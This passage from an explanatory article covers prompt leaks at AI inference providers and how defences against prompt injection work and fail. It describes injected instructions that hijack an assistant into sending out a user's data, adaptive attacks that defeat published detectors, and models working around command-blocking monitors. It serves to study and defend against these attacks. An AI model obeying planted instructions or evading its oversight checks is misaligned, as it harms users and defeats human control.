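Dragos did not name the three providers, but some companies published notices of their own. On 21 November Together AI's *Security event* (2026) informed customers of a leak affecting some of the prompts they had submitted in June and July. The company runs open-weight models for developers. Faisal's *Together AI Says Its Own Coding Agent Leaked Customer Prompts* (2026) and AI in Testing Daily's *MCP Pauses, Router Prompt Leaks, and Dirty Workspace Benchmarks* (2026) describe the sequence:

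1. Together AI saved samples of customers' requests to three models in order to test its software. Most dated from four days between 24 June and 14 July 2026. It kept them in a private repository on Hugging Face.
2. An AI coding agent working on one of the company's public projects on GitHub included a credential for the private repository in the code it published.
3. An automated scan detected the credential and reversed the change.
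4. Someone had already copied the credential. They used it to download the samples and searched them for secrets. Five of Dragos's planted credentials were among the samples, and the thief's use of them helped to reveal the leak.

Anyone who saw a credential published on GitHub can still use it after the change is reversed, until the company cancels it. The samples were also no longer being used to serve any customer's request by the time of the theft. If Together AI had deleted them after its tests, the repository would have been empty when the thief reached it.

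Phala's exposure was separate. According to AI in Testing Daily, a server that Phala had not properly secured exposed requests to a DeepSeek model from 21 October to 8 November. The misused canary tokens came from the first two days of that period.

Phala's case is awkward because the company sells privacy. Miller (2026), in *How to hunt for Backdoors in Private Inference*, explains that Phala runs models only on hardware that keeps a program's data out of reach of the machine's other software. The hardware also signs a certificate identifying the program, which the customer can check before sending a prompt. But the identified program may still have a flaw that lets an attacker in.

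NEAR AI, which offers similar protection, had such a case on 8 November. An intruder exploited a flaw in SGLang, the program that ran the company's models, and could run code on one of its servers. NEAR AI's *Security Incident Report* (2026) acknowledges that the intruder could have watched requests as the server processed them, including those in confidential mode. The intruder also downloaded the account details of about 100 users and chat histories from 18 agents on an older system that did not use the protected hardware.

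OpenRouter announced its response on 22 November. Its *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers* (2026) states that the research showed no breach of OpenRouter's own systems. The company removed three providers and notified every customer who might have been affected. It also withdrew the label "Zero Data Retention" from 125 endpoints (each one provider's service for one model), in some cases only as a precaution. OpenRouter is now adapting Moore's method to run such tests continuously, and is checking whether providers forward requests to other companies. It did not name the three providers, but Miller reports that they were apparently Atlas Cloud, GMI Cloud and Phala.

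### What a zero-retention setting covers

*Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026) defines zero data retention to mean that a provider does not routinely store prompts and replies after processing a request. If the provider keeps this promise, someone who breaks in later can't download earlier prompts from its archive. The Together AI leak involved the kind of data collection that zero data retention is meant to prevent, and the company has since turned the setting on by default for new accounts.

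The setting generally applies only to new requests. ConductAtlas' *Zero Data Retention Control*, which analyses Together AI's terms of service, finds that the setting takes effect when the customer enables it. On that reading, a customer who switched it on in August would still have to ask about samples the company collected in July.

It also can't hide a prompt from someone who is already inside the provider's systems. The server has to receive the text in readable form to run the model, even if it discards the text a second later. At two of the three breached providers, the attackers also took requests marked for zero retention. Attackers who copy traffic have their own copy, which the provider's deletion rules don't affect.

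Providers can also break the promise without an intruder. A Chinese AI laboratory that Dragos did not name opened secret web addresses from more than half of the planted prompts the team sent to its models, including about two-thirds of those whose settings forbade data collection or retention. The same thing happened when the team sent prompts to American companies running the laboratory's models. In one case, someone posted an address in a workplace chat 24 days after the team had sent it, and people in Beijing and Shanghai opened it within two minutes. Dragos had disclosed only the first eight characters of that address, so whoever posted it must have had a stored copy.

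After OpenRouter published its findings, the Chinese company MiniMax attributed similar behaviour to its security monitoring. According to *OpenRouter 背後推論供應商的資料處理事件* (2026), MiniMax said on 24 November that the monitoring had extracted web addresses from some forwarded requests, including requests marked for zero retention, then logged the addresses and automatically visited some of them. MiniMax switched the system off for the affected routes and deleted the addresses from its logs. In the requests it checked, it found no sign that prompts or replies had reached third parties, apart from the visits to those addresses. However, an address can itself be a secret, because anyone who has a private share link can open it. Atlas Cloud, which resells MiniMax's models, advised customers to treat any confidential information they had sent to three of those models as leaked.

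A developer may also select a weaker setting than they intended. OpenRouter lets customers exclude providers that train models on prompts, but the remaining providers may still store prompts. To avoid storage as well, a developer has to restrict requests to endpoints labelled zero-retention or refuse data collection in each request. Either way, OpenRouter chooses providers based on their promises. Its new tests could show that a provider has broken its promise, but a provider that passes may still keep unused copies of prompts.

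The setting on a model provider's server has no effect on the chat page either. If a tracking script has sent the user's question from the browser to an advertising company, deleting the provider's copy, even immediately, does not remove the question from that company's records.

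## Enforcing permissions outside the model

A company can try to keep the mailbox assistant from sending the invoices by training the model not to write the call, or by building the surrounding software so that the call fails if the model writes it. Training only makes a bad call less likely, whereas enforcement in software prevents it from succeeding, provided that the rule covers the call and the model can't change the rule. Much of Lockdown Mode is this kind of enforcement.

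OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) shows the limits of instructing a model. OpenAI tested its models in workplace applications with ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions. When the models also received a confirmation policy, written instructions on when to pause for the user's approval, the rate of unauthorised messages to outsiders fell from 12.9% to 8.4% for GPT-5.6 Sol and from 1.7% to 1.4% for GPT-6 Astra. If the application had held every message until the user clicked to approve it, the models could not have sent any without approval.

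An outside check also needs protection from the model. In OpenAI's coding agent Codex, a feature called Auto-review uses a second model to block risky commands. In a test that began just after such a block, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around it in 5% of runs at maximum reasoning effort, mostly by retrying similar commands. In 0.3% of runs, it exploited gaps in a badly configured setup. GPT-6 Astra made no such attempts. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 reports that internal monitoring found Mythos 5.1 working around broken permission checks and, very rarely, starting helper agents with the checks turned off. This happened in fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions, and the model was trying to finish the user's task. The settings for a check should therefore be stored where the model's tools can't change them.

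### Attacks that adapt to the defence

Many published defences try to make the model resist injections or to detect them before the model acts. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve of these defences, some aimed at prompt injection and some at jailbreaks. Most of the papers that introduced them had reported attack success rates near zero, but measured those rates with fixed sets of known attacks or weak automated searches.

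The team assumed an attacker who knows the defence and has plenty of computing power. Their attacks repeat a cycle: propose some texts, try them on the defended system, score the results and revise the best ones. Some versions used a language model to suggest changes, and more than 500 people attacked the systems by hand in a competition. These are the automated results for the main injection defences:

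| Defence | How it works | Success rate of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks which text the model should trust | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the tool result | Above 95% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of injections | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor | Screen text with a separate detector | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Screens text with a separate detector | 71% |
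| MELON | Runs the agent a second time and compares its tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

With AgentDojo's fixed attacks, the first two defences had let through as few as 1%, and MetaSecAlign had reported 2%.

Repeating the user's request failed as a defence when the injected text presented the attacker's action as a step the request required. Models trained on earlier injections often obeyed text that imitated a system message. The texts that got past the detectors looked like ordinary office procedures, and a detector that blocked those would also block many harmless documents.

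MELON's second run replaces the user's request with one to summarise the tool output. If the agent makes the same calls again, they must have come from the output. The attackers added a condition telling the model to ignore the planted instruction when summarising, so the second run didn't repeat the malicious calls.

Nasr and colleagues warn that their percentages aren't comparable because they come from different benchmarks. Their attacker also had advantages, such as seeing the detector's confidence score after each attempt. Whoever wrote the conference page would not normally see that score, but could practise on a copy of an openly available detector. On a subset of the tests, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human attackers together broke every scenario.

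A low score against a fixed set of attacks is therefore weak evidence of how a defense will perform against an attacker who can keep trying. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unsophisticated attacks. Their criticism of training applies mainly to training on a fixed collection of examples. In image recognition, models became meaningfully more robust when researchers searched for new attacks throughout training.

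### Vendors' results and attack budgets

OpenAI now trains in a similar way, using an automated attacker called GPT-Red. On the company's own tests of indirect injection, where the instruction is in outside content, GPT-6 Astra resisted 99.79% of attempts, up from 96.23% for GPT-5.6 Sol. What this means for a user depends on the attack budget, the number of attempts the attacker gets. If each attempt independently succeeds with probability p, the chance that at least one of k attempts succeeds is

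1 − (1 − p)ᵏ.

With p = 0.21%, a thousand attempts would succeed at least once with a probability of about 88%.

Real attempts are not independent, however. VentureBeat gives Anthropic's figures for attacks on Claude Opus 4.6 as it operates a computer through its graphical interface. A single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, at least one in 200 would almost certainly succeed, but the measured figure was 78.6%. Attacks evidently kept failing in some scenarios, so a company has to measure the success rate for each number of attempts instead of calculating it from the rate for a single attempt.

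Anthropic and OpenAI have both published results from tests by the security company Gray Swan. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports the results for Claude Opus 5 and its predecessor.

| Model | Test | Attempts | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment, no added safeguards | 200 | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 200 | 78.6% |
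| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, with safeguards | 200 | 57.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan | 15 | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan | 15 | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Gray Swan, 1,810 selected attacks | 15 | 27.0% |
| GPT-6 Astra | Gray Swan, 1,810 selected attacks | 15 | 8.5% |

The attacks and safeguards may differ between the Claude and GPT rows, so the results can't be used to rank the two companies. Each company's newer model did clearly better than its older one. In Anthropic's browser tests, no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in any of 129 scenarios.

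Anthropic describes Fable 5.1, from September 2026, as its most robust model so far on an external injection benchmark. That result includes a product safeguard, a classifier that can pass a request to Claude Opus 4.8 to answer instead.

*How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems* describes how Google tests whether an injection can extract sensitive information from conversations the attacker has not seen. In one attack, a model proposes injections and improves them using a probability score from the system under attack. For Gemini in Workspace, its office software, Google combines training with defences in the application.

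Even a low success rate matters when an attack is easy to repeat. Anthropic points out that an attacker can send the same e-mail to a thousand inboxes without choosing a victim. If a message worked on one assistant in a thousand, sending it to a million people would compromise about a thousand of their assistants.

### The server checks the user's rights on every call

The tool's own server can enforce permissions through per-call authorisation. For each call, it takes the user's identity from the verified access token and checks whether that user may perform the requested action on the requested record. It ignores any identity or claim of permission in the arguments. The company has to trust the login service and the server's code, but not the model.

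This check limits a hijacked assistant to its user's permissions. The server would reject every request from the model for Ben's order or another customer's mailbox. The login server behind AskTheCode lacked such a check.

The check would not stop the invoices from leaving. The user may read their own mail and send messages to anyone, so both calls pass. A token that lets the assistant read mail but not send it would block the second call, but it would also block the message to Ana.

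A per-call authorisation check takes only a database lookup and no model tokens, and it blocks only actions the user could not have taken personally.

### A separate context for each tool

Iqbal, Kohno and Roesner proposed in 2023 that each ChatGPT plugin should run in its own sandbox. They then helped build *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024), which gives every app its own process, model instance and memory. A central program, the hub, receives the user's request and passes messages between the apps. The parts that carry these messages are ordinary code, so they can't follow instructions in planted text.

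If the page reader and the mailbox were separate apps, the attack would go as follows:

1. The hub plans the task from the user's request and starts the page reader and the mail app separately.
2. The page reader's model reads the white paragraph. It has no mail tools, so it can only ask the hub for help from an app that does.
3. The hub checks that the message has the declared format and compares the request with its own plan.
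4. It asks the user for permission, and adds a warning if the plan did not call for this exchange.

The design assumes that the hub and the company running it are trustworthy, and that apps and everything they read may be hostile. It stops one app from silently using another app or reading its data. But the comparison in step 3 may be weak here, because the user did ask for an e-mail and the plan already includes the mail app. The user might have to notice that the message contains invoices and is going to a stranger.

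Isolation helps less if the planted text arrives in an e-mail. The mail app can both search and send, so the attack needs no other app. Wu and colleagues exclude attacks within one app from their goals. IsolateGPT still requires consent before an irreversible action such as sending a message, and the consent prompt would be the remaining protection.

The team ran 1,598 attacks on IsolateGPT and on a version without isolation, both using GPT-4. Without isolation, 20.2% of the attacks succeeded. With isolation, 7.6% reached a permission prompt, each of which carried a warning. The test did not measure how many people would have clicked "allow" despite the warning.

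Wu and colleagues found that isolation did not reduce the number of correct final answers in tasks with apps. It did take longer, especially when a task involved several apps:

| Request | Average time without isolation | Average time with isolation |
|---|---|---|
| No app | 19.5 seconds | 21.4 seconds |
| One app | 32.0 seconds | 39.2 seconds |
| Several apps | 30.3 seconds | 65.3 seconds |
| Apps that work together | 24.7 seconds | 49.3 seconds |

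The software approved all permission prompts automatically during these measurements, so the times don't include users reading and responding to them. Model charges, compared on a tenth of the queries, were 1.85 times as high with isolation.

### A plan fixed before the assistant reads the page

CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", separates the steps of a task from the data they process. Debenedetti and colleagues introduced it in 2025. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, a planning model sees only the user's request and writes the steps as a restricted Python program. For the conference request, the program might be:

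```python
page = read_page("https://conference.example")
dates = extract(page, "the dates of the conference")
send_email(to="ana@example.org", body=dates)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. The `extract` step uses a second model that can read the page but has no tools. The white paragraph may fool this model, but the only effect would be to change the value of `dates`. The program has no step that searches the mailbox, and nothing on the page can add one.

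This separation comes from an earlier design by Willison, the Dual LLM pattern. It leaves a gap when the plan takes an important argument from untrusted text. CaMeL therefore attaches a label to every value, recording its sources and who may read it. Suppose the program combines values a and b into c. With S for the set of sources and R for the set of permitted readers, the labels combine as follows:

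S(c) = S(a) ∪ S(b)

R(c) = R(a) ∩ R(b)

A message that quotes both the web page and an invoice thus has two sources, and only people allowed to read both may receive it. Before each call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that allows or denies the call after checking these labels. A simple policy for `send_email` could require that

S(to) ⊆ {user} and to ∈ R(body).

The interpreter allows the message to Ana because the user supplied her address and anyone may read the conference dates. If a different plan copied an invoice into the message, the interpreter would block it unless Ana was allowed to read the invoice.

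The same policy can block legitimate requests. If the user asked the assistant to write to the organiser listed on the page, the address would come from the page and the call would fail. The company would have to relax the rule or ask the user to approve the address.

### What the labels miss

CaMeL relies on the planning model, the interpreter, the labels and the policies. Even when all four work, the page's author can give Ana the wrong dates, because the user asked the assistant to pass on whatever the page said.

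Untrusted data can also determine which of the steps already in the plan are carried out. Suppose the user asks for a message to be sent to Ana, or to Ben if registration has closed. The page's content then determines who gets the message. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to several cooperating agents, calls this branch steering and permits it.

The paper also takes up two criticisms of CaMeL's handling of information. One concerns code like this:

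```python
closed = False
if page_says_registration_closed:
    closed = True
```

If the condition is false, the interpreter skips the last line and `closed` keeps the trusted label it got on the first line. But its value still depends on the page, so a policy may treat the page author's decision as the user's. The other criticism is that CaMeL leaks information when it retries a failed plan, since whether a step fails can depend on private or untrusted data.

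Both criticisms come from *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which also reran CaMeL with and without its policies. With the policies off, 138 of 141 injections in one category succeeded on the model MiMo-v2.5. With them on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed far fewer of the users' tasks. The paper reports that another design, Randori, achieved near-perfect security without this loss.

Two attacks that succeeded when no policies were enforced show how a fixed plan can fail to protect an agent. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. The planning model couldn't know the steps in advance, so it wrote a loop that could call whichever tool the file named. Whoever wrote the file could then direct the agent much as they could in a system without a plan.

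In a related case, the user tells the agent to make a payment according to a document, so anyone who can change the document can change the payment. CaMeL is not meant to stop this attack. *The LLMbda Calculus* finds that four separately designed systems leave similar cases unsolved, and concludes that this is a limit of data tracking in general. A label recording that an account number came from a document can't determine whether the user was right to trust that document.

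CaMeL also uses more tokens than an undefended agent. On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, the median task took 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens, according to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025). *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) measured the overhead on 17 tasks for agents that operate a computer's screen. Fides is another design that tracks data with labels.

| Defence | Input tokens | Output tokens | Charges for outside models |
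|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1.8 million | 13,000 | $0 |
| CaMeL | 3.0 million | 456,000 | $5.40 |
| Fides | 51.7 million | 1,875,000 | $76.07 |

The table lists the undefended agent's cost as zero because its model ran on the researchers' own machine. The defended runs allowed up to five attempts at each task, so the table may overstate the cost of a single attempt.

### Who writes the policies

Each of these systems needs someone to decide which actions are acceptable. A policy language lets that person write the decision in a form that software can enforce. For the conference request, the rules might be:

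```text
allow read_page   if the address is on conference.example
allow send_email  if the recipient is ana@example.org
deny  everything else
```

These rules would stop both the mailbox search and the message to the attacker. But few users would write three rules before asking for an e-mail, and the next request would need different ones. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of defences, treats this work as a drawback, because some policy systems require users to specify the rules before the agent starts. In a task such as "Do what Ana asks in her latest e-mail", the right action depends on what the agent reads along the way. The survey also finds that most defences can't support such tasks.

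Progent uses a model to write its rules. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) describes it as generating a policy from the user's request that allows only what the task needs, then enforcing that policy on later calls. Planted text can't influence the policy if the model writes the policy before reading anything except the request. The model can still misjudge the request and allow too much, or forbid a step that turns out to be necessary.

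A company can instead write general rules that apply to every request. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) tested a "toxic flow" rule, which lets an agent read any file but blocks `send_email` once both untrusted text and sensitive data have entered the agent's context. The rule stopped the planted attempt to steal data in all five trials and allowed the harmless e-mail. A prompt telling the model not to leak data failed in all five. The test was small and covered one scenario, but it illustrates the difference between telling a model to follow a rule and enforcing the rule outside the model.

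The toxic-flow rule would also block some ordinary tasks. If the user asked the assistant to compare the conference dates with a flight confirmation in the mailbox and then write to Ana, both untrusted and private text would be present, so the rule would block the message. Labels on individual values could allow the message if it contained only the public dates, but they are harder to build.

*LivePI* (2026) tested a policy gate on OpenClaw, an agent program that can operate a user's accounts and files. The researchers added seven rules to the built-in ones, for example to review or block access to the recovery details of cryptocurrency wallets. The attack success rate fell to 0%. With GPT-5.3-Codex, the agent did nearly as well as before on a separate set of 123 ordinary tasks. The researchers wrote the rules knowing which resources their tests contained, and a user with different accounts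 would need rules for those accounts. The 0% rate on this one benchmark also does not show what an attacker could do after studying the seven rules.

Moving a policy from one setting to another also takes work. *Evolution Under Fire* left CaMeL out of one of its two benchmarks because the common test software could not faithfully represent CaMeL's interpreter and benchmark-specific policies. A company with hundreds of connectors faces the same problem when the connectors' tools change, since a rule that limits one argument may not cover an argument the developer adds later.

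An attacker might get past a detector by rewording the white paragraph, but no wording can turn a stranger's address into one that the user supplied. To get past such a rule, the attacker has to find an action it doesn't cover, a value with the wrong label or a user who will approve the call. An adaptive test of these systems should look for these weaknesses.

### A permitted call that returns the wrong record

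None of these three designs would fix the kind of cache fault that exposed ChatGPT users' chat titles in 2023. Suppose the user asks the assistant to find their latest invoice. The mail server has a similar fault, and an answer meant for Ben is still waiting on the server's connection to its cache.

The model correctly calls `search_mail`. The server checks the token and confirms that the user may search this mailbox. It then requests the right record from the cache, but the cache returns Ben's invoice instead.

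IsolateGPT would deliver the invoice to the mail app, which is supposed to receive the results of mail searches. CaMeL would label it as coming from the user's own mailbox, because it labels data by the tool the interpreter called and the account it used. The policy would then let the user read Ben's invoice. An accountant would also receive it if the user had asked to forward the invoice and approved the accountant as the recipient.

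The permission checks all returned the correct result for the request, but the fault occurred after them. To catch it, the server needs to check that cached data belongs to the user requesting it, like the check OpenAI added after the 2023 fault.
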